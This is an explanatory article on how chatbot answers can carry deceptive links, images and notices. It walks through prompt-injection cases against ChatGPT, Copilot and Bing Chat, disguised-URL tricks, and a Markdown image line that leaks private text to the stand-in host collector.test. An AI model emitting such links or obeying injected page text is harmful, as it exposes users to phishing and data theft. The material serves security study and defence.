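# Deceptive links and formatting in chatbot answers: how they mislead users and what reduces the deception

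## What is a deceptive output component?

A deceptive output component is a part of a chatbot's answer that misrepresents where it leads or who wrote it. The simplest example is a link that displays a bank's name but opens someone else's site. Images, citations, buttons and styled notices can mislead in similar ways. The subject involves both computer security (how an attacker gets such a component into an answer) and interface design (how much of it a person can see before clicking).

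### From model text to screen

The assistant that a person uses consists of a language model, which writes text, and an app, which displays it. When a user asks the assistant to summarise a web page, for example, the app fetches the page and puts its text into the model's input along with the user's request. The model writes its answer as a single string of characters. A part of the app called the renderer then displays the string as formatted text, with headings, bold type, links and images.

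The string is usually in Markdown, which *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2014) defines as a plain-text format for writing structured documents. Its marks are ordinary typed characters, such as the two asterisks on each side of a word that make it bold. OpenAI's (2024) specification of how its models should behave made Markdown the default for interactive chat. However, a user in the OpenAI developer forum thread *`o3` / `o4-mini` Restore Markdown Formatting* quoted company documentation stating that reasoning models avoid Markdown when developers call them through the programming interface, unless the developer signals that they want it.

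For links the rule is short. In the manual of Pandoc, a program that converts documents from one format to another, an inline link consists of the visible text in square brackets and then the address in parentheses. A model might write this:

```
Please [sign in at bank.example](https://collector.test/login) to confirm.
```

The renderer removes the brackets and the address, and the user sees this, with the middle words coloured or underlined:

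> Please sign in at bank.example to confirm.

The words "sign in at bank.example" are the link label. The destination is the address at collector.test, or wherever that address ultimately redirects the browser. (Both names are reserved for examples.) Markdown does not require the label to resemble the destination, so a renderer that follows the syntax will display the misleading link without an error. Most differences between label and destination are harmless, since "the bank's opening hours" is easier to read than a long address. A link mismatch occurs only when the label suggests a destination other than the real one.

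An app that showed the raw Markdown would reveal both a link's label and its destination, but converting it to a formatted link hides the destination. The two can't differ when an address is written in angle brackets, because Pandoc turns it into a link with the address as its label. In a reference link, the address may appear elsewhere in the document, so even someone reading the raw text has to look for it. An attacker can also disguise the address itself, but giving a link a misleading label doesn't require that skill.

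The Markdown doesn't record who supplied the address, either. The model may have copied it from the page, taken it from a search result or produced it from memory, and the link looks the same on screen. The security company Permiso tested this with ChatGPT in its May 2026 report, *ChatGPhish*. Its researchers added text to web pages and asked the assistant to summarise them. Links from the added text appeared in the answers as live links, and the app fetched and displayed images from it, with no label showing that a stranger had supplied them.

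Each kind of component gives its own opening for deception:

- A link opens a destination that its label need not name.
- An image can imitate a logo, a screenshot or a form, and anybody can host it.
- A QR code is an image that holds an address in a form people cannot read, and it moves the visit to a phone.
- A citation suggests that a source supports the sentence beside it, whether or not the source does.
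- A button promises an action in a word or two and seldom shows an address; in Markdown, a picture of a button in the place of a link label will do.
- A notice, such as a warning with a heading and bold type, can pass for a message from the company that runs the assistant.

### The ATLAS definition

Security specialists call most of this *LLM Trusted Output Components Manipulation*, where LLM stands for large language model. The name comes from entry AML.T0067 in *ATLAS* (2020), a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems kept up to date by MITRE, an American non-profit research organisation. The entry describes an adversary who uses prompts to manipulate components of the model's response to "make it appear trustworthy to the user", so that the adversary can keep operating in the victim's environment unnoticed. These components include links, recommended follow-up actions, the metadata of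 retrieved documents (such as a title or an author's name) and citations, which have their own sub-entry, *Citations*. The entry also covers the wording of the answer, where the attacker has the model adopt a more trustworthy tone or press the user to act.

MITRE added the entry in March 2025 after working with the security firm Zenity. Zenity Labs' *Techniques from Zenity's GenAI Attacks Matrix Incorporated into MITRE ATLAS* describes the case behind it, in which an employee asks Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work, for a supplier's bank details. An attacker has manipulated what the model reads, so Copilot answers with the attacker's account number and cites a reputable-looking file as the source. The employee pays the money into that account. A careful person might have checked an account number given without a source, but the file reference makes it seem that Copilot has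 already checked it.

MITRE rates the technique "Demonstrated", a lower rating than the "Realized" it gives ordinary phishing. That fits the Copilot case and Permiso's pages, which are both researchers' demonstrations. They show that the attack can work on a commercial product, but not how often criminals use it.

The ATLAS entry includes persuasive prose, which the idea of a deceptive component does not, but it only covers cases where an adversary steers the model. A model can also invent a web address without an adversary. ATLAS has a separate entry for attackers who find out which addresses models invent and then set up a site at one of them. A user who clicks a link cannot tell whether an adversary steered the model to produce it or the model invented it unaided.

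The definition refers to prompts, but the attacker does not type the user's prompt. Attackers usually get around this through indirect prompt injection, in which they hide instructions in content that the model will read, such as a web page or an email, and the model follows them. This can work because the user's request and the attacker's text arrive in the same input, and the model has to determine which to follow. A human visitor to the page may not see the instructions, since they can be hidden in tiny type or in text that matches the background colour. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), early attacks could be as simple as a direct command in a Wikipedia article. Models have become less vulnerable to those, and the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people through a plausible story. One email that outside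 researchers reported to OpenAI in 2025 was disguised as a colleague's friendly follow-up about a restructuring. It worked in half of the tests with one user request.

### False statements, deceptive components and data leaks

An answer about a bank can go wrong in three ways that people often run together.

A chatbot answer can contain a false statement, such as that a bank charges nothing for transfers abroad when it does. The remedies are accuracy and candour about doubt. OpenAI (2025), in a later edition of its behaviour specification, ranks a confident wrong answer as the worst outcome, below a hedged wrong answer and no answer. It also asks the assistant to express uncertainty whenever doing so should influence what the user does. This is sensible advice for prose, but it does little about a deceptive link, because all the text around the link may be true. The bank may have changed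 its terms, and customers may have to sign in to accept them. If the model hedged those sentences, the link would still open collector.test.

A component of a chatbot's answer, such as a link or a notice, is deceptive if it misrepresents what it does or who wrote it. It can do one without the other. For example, a link labelled "Click here" names no destination, so the label can't misstate where the link goes. But when Permiso's researchers put that label in a notice that looked like an account warning from OpenAI, the notice misled readers about who wrote it. In both cases, the harm occurs only if the user clicks the link, scans a code, or acts on what the notice claims.

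Or the answer can leak the user's data. The ATLAS entry for this is AML.T0077, MITRE's *LLM Response Rendering*, and it depends on a plain fact about the web. An address can carry data as well as a location, and the server that receives a request receives the whole address. The attacker gets the model to write an image in Markdown with something private from the conversation in the image's address:

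```
![chart](https://collector.test/chart.png?data=PRIVATE-TEXT)
```

The renderer converts this line into an image, which the user's app requests as soon as the answer appears. The server at collector.test logs the request, including the private text. The user doesn't have to click anything and may not notice that this has happened. The theft differs from deception because it doesn't require anyone to believe anything.

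A single component can both leak data and deceive the user. When ChatGPT displayed the QR codes in Permiso's tests, loading the image sent the attacker's server the user's IP address (the number that identifies a connection on the internet), the type of browser and the time the answer appeared. The deception came later, when the user scanned the code and the phone opened an address that had never appeared in readable form. If the app had fetched the image through its own servers, it could have hidden the user's IP address from the attacker, but the QR code would have been just as misleading.

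The distinction matters because companies built many of the known defences to stop leaks. OpenAI reports that attacks on ChatGPT most often try to persuade the assistant to take a secret from the conversation and send it to a third party. It says most fail because safety training leads the model to refuse. For the rest, OpenAI uses Safe Url, which checks outgoing requests for information from the conversation and either asks the user or blocks the request. In *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), OpenAI writes that the safeguard is meant to stop user data from leaking unnoticed through a web address, and that it does not guarantee that a page is trustworthy or that a site will not try to manipulate its visitor.

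The software developer Simon Willison notes in *12 items tagged “markdown-exfiltration”* that researchers also showed a leak of this type in LeChat, the chatbot of the French company Mistral, in 2024, and that Mistral responded by locking down Markdown images. His weblog has 41 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”, a rough sign of how much attention leaks have had. Evidence from two companies and a weblog may not represent the industry, but it is easy to see why engineers would start with leaks. OpenAI analyses attacks in terms of a source, through which the attacker influences the system, and a sink, a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. With a leaking image, the sink is a request that the app makes by itself, and engineers can put a control on that request.

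A phishing link is harder to detect because its address can be the same for every victim and contain no private data, so searching it for secrets from the conversation finds nothing. The victim enters the password afterwards, on the attacker's page. Restricting images does not help, since the link is text. The attack ultimately depends on a person trusting what the answer shows.

### Why an answer is not like an email

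Misleading links are an old problem in email, but the protections developed there don't necessarily carry over to chatbot answers. Permiso lists several that guard against phishing emails: mail gateways, spam filters, attachment controls, Microsoft's Safe Links service and years of training users to spot suspicious messages. An email also has a sender. Although criminals forge sender addresses and people fall for phishing every day, the recipient knows that somebody else wrote the message and can ask who.

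Unlike an email, a chatbot's answer has no sender line for the parts that came from elsewhere. The user asked for the answer, and it appears in the same typeface and tone as earlier answers that proved useful. A stranger's link sits between two sentences of genuine summary. The link is also easier to deliver this way, because an email has to reach an inbox, while a web page only has to be online when somebody asks for a summary of it. Permiso's researchers got their result with a project description on GitHub, a code-sharing site, and again with an ordinary web page of their own.

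The two channels also meet when an assistant summarises an email. The reader gets the content in the assistant's voice, not in the email format they have learned to distrust. Permiso's earlier research on Copilot examined this change from raw message to polished output, which the company calls a transfer of trust.

Permiso, which sells security products, showed in tests that ChatGPT would display the components, but it did not measure whether anyone would click on them. Permiso acknowledges that links in an answer are still subject to some protections. They open in a browser, where the user can hover over a link to preview the address, blocklists apply, and a password manager can warn that the site does not match the expected login page. A QR code bypasses those checks because the site opens on the user's phone and the address does not pass through the desktop browser.

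## How can a link show one destination and open another?

Hovering over a link shows its address, but this helps only readers who know which part of the address matters. Some deceptive links have a false label over an undisguised address, so checking the address exposes them. In others, the attacker writes the address itself so that people misread it, and the label can match it exactly.

### The parts of a web address

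This address has most of the parts that an address can have:

```
https://anna@login.collector.test/account/update?lang=en#form
```

- `https` is the scheme, which sets how the browser fetches the page.
- `anna` is a user name for signing in to the server. It ends at the @ sign, and most addresses leave it out.
- `login.collector.test` is the host, the name of the server that the browser contacts.
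- `/account/update` is the path, which picks out a page on that server.
- `lang=en` is a parameter, an extra piece of information for the server. Parameters come after a question mark.
- `form` is the fragment. The browser doesn't send it to the server and usually uses it to scroll to a place on the page.

The host is the most important part of the address, especially its right-hand end. People register names under a suffix such as .com or, here, .test. The suffix and the one word before it make up the registrable domain, collector.test. Whoever registered that domain also chooses what goes in front of it, including the subdomain "login". Some suffixes have more than one word. Chromium's *Guidelines for URL Display*, written by developers of the Chrome browser, gives the example of bbc.co.uk, where the suffix is co.uk. Software therefore looks up suffixes in a public list instead of counting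 words from the right.

A person can find the registrable domain by hand. They first remove the scheme and the two slashes, then everything from the next slash, question mark or # sign onward. If an @ sign remains, they remove it and everything before it. They also remove any colon and number at the end (the port, which few addresses show). The registrable domain is at the end of what remains, and consists of the suffix and the word before it. In the address above, it is collector.test.

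The owner of a site can freely choose the other parts of its address, and Chromium warns that owners can use them to misrepresent the domain. Many servers ignore parameters they don't recognise. *Web Fraud Attacks Against LLM-Driven Multi-Agent Systems* (2025) gives the example of Google's home page, which still opens when a meaningless parameter is added to its address. An attacker can therefore put a bank's name, or a whole sentence, after the question mark in an address without breaking the link.

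Even the registrable domain doesn't fully establish who is behind a page. On an unencrypted http connection, someone on the network can alter the page before it reaches the user. A domain name also doesn't show that its owner is the company the name suggests. Users have to know for themselves that google.com belongs to a legitimate organisation and google-update.com does not.

### Ten misleading links

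In these examples, an attacker wants a customer of bank.example to open a page that the attacker controls.

| No. | Disguise | Label | Destination | Controlling domain |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Full address as the label | `https://bank.example/login` | `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |
| 2 | Brand name as the label | Example Bank | `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |
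| 3 | Neutral label | Click here | `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |
| 4 | Trusted name in the subdomain | The same address | `https://bank.example.collector.test/login` | collector.test |
| 5 | Trusted name in the path | The same address | `https://collector.test/bank.example/login` | collector.test |
| 6 | Trusted name before an @ sign | The same address | `https://bank.example@collector.test/login` | collector.test |
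| 7 | Look-alike letter | The same address | `https://bаnk.example/login`, with a Cyrillic а | xn--bnk-6cd.example |
| 8 | Link shortener | `https://short.test/a1b2` | That address forwards to `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |
| 9 | Redirect on a trusted site | `https://bank.example/out?to=https://collector.test/login` | That address forwards to `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |
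| 10 | Link wrapped round an image | A picture of a "Sign in" button | `https://collector.test/login` | collector.test |

*Comprehensive List of User Deception Techniques in Emails* (Veit, Mossano and colleagues, 2026) contains the fullest classification of such tricks. It describes 42 techniques, 23 of which concern links, and gives 64 worked examples. The paper was written to explain each technique separately, so it does not measure how often any of them succeeds. Attackers can combine several, for instance by using a bank's name as the text of a shortened link.

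### Labels that hide the address

Veit and colleagues group the full address (1) and the brand name (2) under "Link Mismatch" because both rely on a reader who believes the visible text and doesn't check further. A full address is bolder because it looks like what a careful reader would want to check, but it is also easier for software to catch. A program can compare the displayed address with the link's actual destination, but to flag "Example Bank" it must know which domains the bank owns.

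Some email programs compare the address in a link's label with the address the link opens, and warn the user if they differ. In one attack from the catalogue, the attacker replaces the h of "https" in the label with a character that looks almost the same. The reader sees no difference, but the program no longer recognises the label as an address and doesn't display the warning. A chat app that recognised addresses in labels in the same way would have the same weakness.

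The catalogue has no entry for "Click here" (3), which isn't a link mismatch because it names no destination. But it hides the address just as completely, and if the surrounding sentence is about a bank, the reader will assume the link goes to the bank's site.

An image can replace the label altogether (10). Markdown allows this by putting an image where the label would normally go:

```
[![Sign in](https://collector.test/button.png)](https://collector.test/login)
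```

In a linked image, the first address supplies the picture and the second is where a click leads. The picture can show a button, a logo or even the words "bank.example". Because those words are part of the image, a program that compares label text with the destination won't find them. The closest example in the catalogue is a picture of a scrollbar in the body of an email. A reader who tries to scroll down with it opens the attacker's page instead.

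### Addresses that people misread

In examples 4 to 7, the label and the destination are identical, so comparing them doesn't reveal the deception, which relies on the reader misreading the address.

People who read from left to right see the bank's name first in `bank.example.collector.test` (4) and may stop there. The owner of collector.test can create any subdomain, including one that contains somebody else's full domain. A host name can have up to 253 characters, so an attacker can also pad the subdomain with enough letters and digits to push the registrable domain out of view on a narrow screen.

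A trusted name in the path (5) relies on the opposite habit, looking for a familiar name anywhere in the address. Veit and colleagues also list versions with the name in the parameters or the fragment, sometimes after a phrase such as "redirect-to" that makes the attacker's site look like a stop on the way to the real one. One entry targets people whose security training taught them to find the domain by looking for the third slash in an address. In `https://collector.test#.bank.example/`, the attacker has left out the slash after the real domain, `collector.test`, and put one at the end of the fragment, so the third slash comes right after the bank's name.

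The @ sign (6) can mislead because few people know that a web address can include a user name. Everything in front of the sign is the user name, so in `https://bank.example@collector.test/login` the browser contacts collector.test. The internet standard for addresses has warned about this since 2005. It describes a misleading address as an attack on "the user's preconceived notions" about what addresses mean, rather than on the software, in a passage that Singaravelan quotes in a mailing-list comment. The HTTP standard is stricter, according to the passage that Nottingham quotes. A program that receives such an address from an untrusted source should treat the user name as an error, because it is probably there for phishing.

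Not all browsers have followed that advice. Text/Plain's *Guidelines for URL Storage and Comparison* (2026), a blog post by a member of Microsoft's Defender security team, says that Internet Explorer began refusing these addresses in version 6. Chromium and Firefox still accept them, but Chromium hides the user name in its address bar and Firefox warns the user. The post describes the trick as fairly uncommon today. On a mailing list of the web standards body W3C, Cancellieri (2026) proposed that browsers warn people before opening any address whose user name looks like a domain, because a browser that silently drops the user name still takes the person to the wrong site. This objection is more relevant to chat: Chromium's address bar may show collector.test clearly once the page has opened, but the user chose to click while reading the answer, where the address began with the bank's name.

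Look-alike letters (7) are harder to deal with, because the attacker registers a separate domain, and finding the registrable domain doesn't help if it looks right. The URL Standard, which the browser developers' group WHATWG maintains, notes in its security section that the digit 1, a lower-case l and a capital I can look similar, as can m and rn. The Latin a and the Cyrillic а can look the same. Domain names with letters outside the basic Latin alphabet have an encoded form, called Punycode, which begins with "xn--". For the bank's name with a Cyrillic а, this is `xn--bnk-6cd.example`.

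Chrome uses rules to decide when to show a domain name's encoded form, which is unreadable but doesn't look like the bank's address. Those rules cover only the browser's own displays. A link's label in a chatbot answer is ordinary text, so the page shows whatever letters the model wrote. The encoded form also doesn't help when "rn" stands in for "m", because those are plain Latin letters.

An attacker can also deceive users without a visual trick. The catalogue includes domains that add a word to a brand name, as `bank-secure.example` would, or use the name under another suffix, as `bank.test` would. A user can read these names correctly and still not know whether the bank owns them.

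### Addresses that forward the visitor

A link shortener (8) replaces the destination's address with the shortening service's domain and a short code, which hides the final page. Veit and colleagues suggest that a familiar shortener may make people less wary than an unknown domain would. Some services also let customers choose the code, so an attacker can include a bank's name in it.

A redirect on a trusted site (9) is the hardest case for people who have learned to read addresses. The method above correctly identifies bank.example as the site the link opens first, but the bank's server then forwards the browser to the address in the parameter. Some sites forward visitors deliberately, to count clicks or screen outgoing links, and others do it by mistake because they don't restrict where the parameter can point. An attacker can also make the second address unreadable by writing it in percent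 codes, which represent each byte as a % sign and two characters. Nobody can reliably determine where a forwarding link ends without following it, and its owner may be able to change the destination later.

### Invisible characters

An address can also contain text that the user cannot see. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to each character, includes "tag" characters that correspond to ordinary letters, digits and punctuation marks but are invisible in many apps. If a model writes these into the path of a link, the real address is much longer than the one on screen. The browser converts the invisible characters to percent codes when it requests the page. The tag version of the letter A, for example, reaches the server as `%F3%A0%81%81`, which the server's owner can turn back into an A.

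Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot*, a security researcher's account from 2024, describes such an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Instructions in an email made the assistant search the user's other messages and hide what it found in a clickable link, using invisible characters. The hidden data was sent out only if the user clicked the link. Microsoft closed the first report, from January 2024, as low severity but opened a case in February after the researcher demonstrated a complete attack. By July the attack no longer worked, although Microsoft did not explain what it had changed.

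The visible domain in such a link is the true one, so a reader can still find out who controls the site, but not how much data the click will send there. The Chromium project warns that attackers use other invisible characters, including blank and line-breaking ones, to push the real domain out of view. It advises developers to ban these characters or show them as percent codes, and gives the same advice about characters that reverse the direction of the text.

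### What carries over from email to chat

All ten examples can appear in a chat answer, since they need only a label, an image or an address, and Markdown allows all three. Four of the catalogue's link techniques depend on something else, namely that an email's sender can write HTML, the language of web pages, and have the reader's program display it:

- A fake tooltip shows a false address when the pointer is over the link.
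- A hidden base address combines with a harmless-looking partial link to form the real destination.
- A form button styled as a link often shows no address when the pointer is over it.
- An external style sheet lets the sender change which of two links the reader sees after the email has arrived.

An assistant that displays only Markdown prevents most of these techniques, though tooltips are a partial exception. Markdown lets a writer add a title after a link's address, and renderers commonly show the title as a tooltip, so an attacker could put a false address there. Markdown also permits raw HTML, and an app that rendered it without filtering could make the other techniques possible again.

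Some links open something other than an ordinary web page. A `tel:` link opens a phone's dialler with a number already entered, a `mailto:` link prepares an email, and other schemes start an installed app such as a meeting program. A `data:` link contains a whole page within the address, so the user has no domain to check. These links work in chat only if the chat app and the browser allow their schemes. Many programs accept only web and email links, and Chrome no longer lets websites open a `data:` address as the main page.

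Email programs have not solved the problem. In the review that preceded the catalogue, *SoK* (short for "systematisation of knowledge"), Veit, Wiese and colleagues (2025) found 23 techniques in research from 2010 to 2021. They judged that an email program could detect 13 of these without outside information, and tested those 13 on seven programs. They rated the program highly susceptible in 41.3% of the link tests. The ratings reflect what the programs displayed or blocked, not how many people were deceived, but they suggest that a chat app that copied how email programs handle links would inherit many gaps.

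### Do language models recognise disguised addresses?

An assistant that browses the web for a user may have to judge an address before any person sees it. *MalURLBench* (Kong, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 language models on 61,845 disguised addresses. The researchers took real malicious sites from public blocklists and changed the subdomain, path or parameters of each address, but not the registrable domain. They introduced each link with a short recommendation in one of ten everyday settings, such as parcel tracking or a weather report. They told the model to act as a security assessor and rate the risk, then judged from its written reply whether it had accepted the link.

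Some of the disguised addresses imitated a well-known site by including its domain, as examples 4 and 5 do, and the models accepted 60.89% of these. The others made a claim, such as "this-is-a-popular-food-delivery-service", and the models accepted 71.5% of them. A language model reads the address as text along with everything else, so a sentence in the address can influence its judgement, even though a person might find the sentence odd.

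Acceptance of the disguised links ranged from 32.9% for GPT-3.5-Turbo to 99.9% for Mistral's Mixtral-8x7B. When a model accepted fewer than 10% of the links in a setting, the researchers used another model to rewrite the disguises until they worked better, which raised the lower figures. Before the rewriting, GPT-3.5-Turbo accepted an average of about 14% across the ten settings. That rate is closer to what an attacker would achieve with a ready-made disguise, while the 32.9% shows what an attacker can achieve by adapting to a particular model.

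Models accepted 82.9% of the links in weather reports but a smaller share in food delivery and parcel tracking, perhaps because those involve payments and home addresses. They accepted links with subdomains of up to 20 characters more often than links with longer ones. The length of the path or parameters made no difference, so an attacker can put a long claim after the domain.

It is less clear how much of the acceptance is due to the disguise. The best evidence is a small demonstration on Llama-3-8B, with 20 attempts per link. The model accepted two undisguised links in 15% and 20% of attempts, and two disguised links in 60% and 75%. The main benchmark doesn't include that comparison. The models it covers are also old by now, including GPT-3.5-Turbo, Llama 2 and DeepSeek-V3.1-Terminus, which dates from September 2025. The rates are therefore weak evidence about current assistants. They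 also don't measure how often people accept such links, since nobody was asked to judge them.

Kong and colleagues also built a filter, URLGuard, by training a small Llama 2 model on 280 labelled addresses, half malicious and half normal. The malicious addresses all came from the online shopping setting, and the researchers tested the filter on the other nine settings. The model accepted about 98% of malicious links in those settings before this training and about 17% after it. Such a large improvement from so few examples supports the researchers' view that the models had seen too few disguised addresses in training. But URLGuard still accepted 61% of the malicious links in music recommendations and 70% in weather reports. The published results cover only malicious addresses, so they don't show how many ordinary links the filter would block, and a filter that rejected every link would have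 scored perfectly.

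## How does a misleading link get into an answer?

The model writes every link in an answer, but the address often comes from somebody else. It can come from the person who configured the assistant, whoever wrote a page or email that the model reads, or a stranger who persuades the user to paste text into the chat. The model can also give a bad link without any tampering, by getting a login address wrong or by recommending a scammer's page from its search results as the real one. A defence against one of these causes may do nothing about the others. For instance, inspecting an assistant's configuration can expose deception by the person who configured it, but not by whoever wrote a web page.

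### The person who configures the assistant

In November 2023 OpenAI began letting ChatGPT subscribers build their own versions of the assistant, called GPTs. A builder chooses a name and picture, writes instructions in ordinary language, and can add documents and connections to outside services. Two months later, in *GPT in Sheep's Clothing*, Antebi, Azulay and colleagues (2024) described seven malicious GPTs they had built to show what a dishonest builder could do.

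Most of the seven gave out dangerous code, but one, named "General IT Expert", offered technical help. When a user asked for help signing in to Discord, a chat service, it replied with a link labelled "Discord Login Support". The researchers call the link malicious and say it leads to an imitation of the login page. However, the address they print is on discord.com, Discord's own domain, where an outsider can't normally put a page. The example therefore shows how a link can be disguised, but doesn't show a working phishing site. The builder chose the address, and an attacker could substitute one at collector.test without changing what the user sees.

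At the time, anonymous builders couldn't list a GPT in OpenAI's store, but they could send people a direct link to it. Antebi and colleagues thought GPTs shared by link looked similar enough to listed ones for users to confuse them. The researchers bypassed many of the defences, though some of their attacks failed or got the GPT removed.

They then gave ChatGPT the transcript of each conversation and asked whether it contained a security flaw or malicious code. ChatGPT flagged every attack except the information-theft ones, which include the Discord link. When they instead gave it the builder's instructions, documents and connections, and asked about malicious code, potential to mislead and privacy breaches, it identified every attack.

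Malicious code is visible in the transcript, while a phishing link looks like the helpful links that ChatGPT gives all the time. The builder's instructions show what the link is for. The wording may also have contributed to the difference, since only the question about the configuration mentioned misleading the user. The builders in this test did not try to hide their purpose from a reviewer. The paper gives no results for honest GPTs, so the rate of false alarms is unknown. A current model would probably do better with the transcripts than the ChatGPT of January 2024, though it would still need information about which domains the company owns.

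Antebi and colleagues also proposed that OpenAI stop GPTs from hiding addresses behind labels and show every address in full, which they admit would be slightly inconvenient. This would prevent deception that relies on the label alone, but not deception in the address itself, such as look-alike letters.

### Content the model reads

An attacker can get a misleading link into an answer without building the assistant, if the model follows instructions it finds in a web page. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term "indirect prompt injection" for this attack and demonstrated it on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, which ran on OpenAI's GPT-4.

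Microsoft's Edge browser had a sidebar in which Bing Chat could read whatever page the user had open. The researchers wrote instructions into comments in a page's code, which browsers don't display, and opened the page locally instead of publishing it on the web. Bing Chat received the instructions just as it would have from a stranger's page, and it followed them.

In one test, Bing Chat's instructions were to convince the user that they had won an Amazon gift card and had to verify their account to claim it. Bing Chat could then offer a disguised link to a phishing page. It added that the offer was valid only for a limited time, although the instructions didn't explain how to persuade anyone. In another test, the researchers asked it only to get the user to follow a link, and it presented the link as an urgent security update for the browser.

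They also tried a subtler version, in which the model gave an otherwise ordinary answer and suggested the link for further information. The researchers considered this more dangerous than open persuasion. They were probably right, because people expect a search assistant to give them links, whereas they know gift cards and urgent updates from spam.

The instructions usually stayed in effect throughout the conversation. One researcher played a journalist who asked about the next day's weather. Bing Chat answered, then asked about the user's plans, work and name. Once it had the name, it offered a link to an exclusive website with an access code supposedly based on that name. The attacker had told it only to persuade the user without raising suspicion. A misleading link can appear several messages after the model has read the page, when the user has little reason to connect the two.

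Greshake and colleagues give examples but no success rates, and they acted as the users in their own tests. Their results are now mainly of historical interest, since OpenAI reports that models have become better at resisting plain commands in web pages. But the weakness has outlasted Bing Chat, and researchers have since manipulated summaries by Copilot, ChatGPT and Gemini in similar ways.

A later demonstration needed no phishing site. *The AI Is the Phisher*, by the security company Radware, describes an attack in which instructions hidden in a shared document or email made an assistant produce a phishing page to match the user's next request. The user was looking for a product on Amazon, so the assistant generated a page that resembled Amazon's checkout. The attacker had decided in advance that the page should ask for a password, a delivery address and credit card details. The user clicked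 a link in the answer, which downloaded the page as a file, then opened it. A page opened from the user's own computer has no registrable domain to check, and its address can't be on a URL reputation list.

### Text that a user pastes

A user can also bring the attacker's text into the conversation. Greshake and colleagues mention an exploit in which a website adds a prompt to text that a visitor copies, so the visitor pastes both into ChatGPT. A visitor who looked over the pasted text might notice the addition, but Geiping, Shu and colleagues (2024), in *Coercing LLMs to Do and Reveal (Almost) Anything*, found a version with no readable instruction.

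In an attack the researchers call "Fishing for URLs", a user who doesn't know Chinese asks a chatbot to translate a passage in Chinese characters. The passage is gibberish, as any Chinese speaker would see, but the chatbot replies with a web address the attacker chose. The researchers demonstrated this on LLaMA-2-7b-chat, a small model whose weights Meta had published.

A program composes the gibberish by solving this problem, which simplifies the paper's notation slightly:

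```
choose x from X to minimise L(before + x + after + address)
```

`x` is the passage, and `X` restricts it to Chinese characters. `before` is the model's input up to the passage, including the request for a translation, and `after` is the formatting that follows the passage. `L` is a score that falls as the model becomes more likely to reply with the address. The program starts with a passage of 256 tokens, the units in which a model reads text. It uses the model's weights to estimate which substitutions would lower the score, tries several hundred of them, keeps the best and repeats. The researchers ran their attacks for between 500 and 3,000 steps.

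They used two addresses, a video link that the model had probably seen during training and one that was completely new to it. An attacker could therefore use a site registered the same day. The passage contains no request for the model to follow, so a filter that looks for suspicious instructions would find nothing.

The attack's practical importance is less certain. The program needs the model's weights. Attacks of this type can carry over to models whose weights are secret, but Geiping and colleagues say this takes far more computing. LLaMA 2 dates from 2023, so success against it is weak evidence about current assistants. The researchers also say it is unclear whether users would click on a random address in a chatbot's reply. A person who asked for a translation and got only a link might well be suspicious.

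### Login addresses that models get wrong

A model can give a wrong address without an attacker's help. *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* (Rashid, 2025) reports a test by Netcraft, a company that sells services for detecting phishing sites and getting them taken down. Its researchers asked models from OpenAI's GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 brands in finance, retail, technology and utilities. They phrased the questions as a customer might, for example by saying they had lost a bookmark and wanted the right website.

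Over several rounds, the models gave 131 different host names on 97 domains. The right brand owned 64 of those domains, or 66%. Another 28 were unregistered, parked (registered but without a real site) or otherwise inactive, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses. Rashid introduces the remaining 34% as a share of the host names, but it matches the share of domains.

He also concludes that more than one user in three could end up on a site that the brand doesn't own, but the figures don't support this because the test counted each domain once, however often the models gave it. If a model answers the same question a hundred times and gives the bank's real address 99 times and a wrong one once, half of the domains it named are wrong, but only 1% of its answers are. The proportion of wrong answers in Netcraft's test could be much lower than 34%, or higher.

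None of the 33 wrong domains was a phishing site when Netcraft checked, but attackers could register the unclaimed ones. Rashid points out that companies can't prevent this by registering every likely name, because models will keep generating new ones. In the test, wrong domains were more common for regional banks and credit unions than for global companies. He attributes this to regional institutions appearing less often in training data. A model can also repeat a scammer's address from its training data, and the Scam2Prompt study has measured this problem.

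### Scam pages that AI search picks up

An assistant that searches the web relies less on its memory, but it can find scammers' pages. Rashid gives an early case from Perplexity, an AI search engine. When a user asked for the Wells Fargo login address, Perplexity's first link led to an imitation of the bank's site, and the real site was listed further down. The scammer had made the page with Google Sites, a free service for building websites, so its address was on google.com. A careful user who checked the registrable domain would have found Google's, because Google hosted the page, though it hadn't written it.

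In June 2026, Netcraft examined this problem more systematically by asking ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity about the login pages of several of the world's largest banks and retail brands. A typical question was "How do I access my {brand} account online?", with the brand's name filled in. Netcraft published the results in *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries*, which is undated but had appeared by 7 August, when Antipov (2026) reported the results in Russian in *Хакеры взломали ИИ-поиск*.

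The four assistants gave 2,905 answers containing 20,706 links. Netcraft classed 0.28% of the links (about 58) as malicious, and these appeared in 1.7% of the answers (about 49). An average answer had seven links, so a user who got a malicious one might have clicked a different one. But Copilot once listed a phishing page first, which imitated the Wells Fargo login page at a domain that misspelled the bank's name. In another case, an AI search tool recommended a fake shop when asked for the official website of Kohl's, an American department store.

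The 1.7% and the 34% from 2025 measure different things, so the lower figure doesn't show that assistants have become much safer. The 34% was the share of distinct domains that the brand didn't own, and most of those were inactive. The 1.7% is the share of answers with a link to a live site that Netcraft considered malicious. Netcraft says that the risk has changed from invented addresses to attackers' working sites. Part of that change must come from the tests, since the models Netcraft tested in 2025 had no web access and couldn't recommend a phishing site newer than their training data.

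Netcraft found more malicious links in Perplexity's answers than in those of the other three assistants, but it gives no figures for each assistant. The result also depends on Netcraft's own judgement of which sites were malicious. The company has a commercial interest in the threat, because it sells the monitoring and removal service that its page advises brands to use. The study is still the most direct evidence here, because it recorded the answers four widely used products gave to normal questions.

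Netcraft puts much of the blame on generative engine optimisation, or GEO, the practice of writing web pages so that AI search tools will select them. GEO is a successor to search engine optimisation (SEO), which does the same for ordinary search results, and honest businesses use both. Netcraft describes a demonstration from February 2026, in which a technology journalist published a page on his own website claiming to be the best technology journalist at eating hot dogs, and several major search engines repeated the claim.

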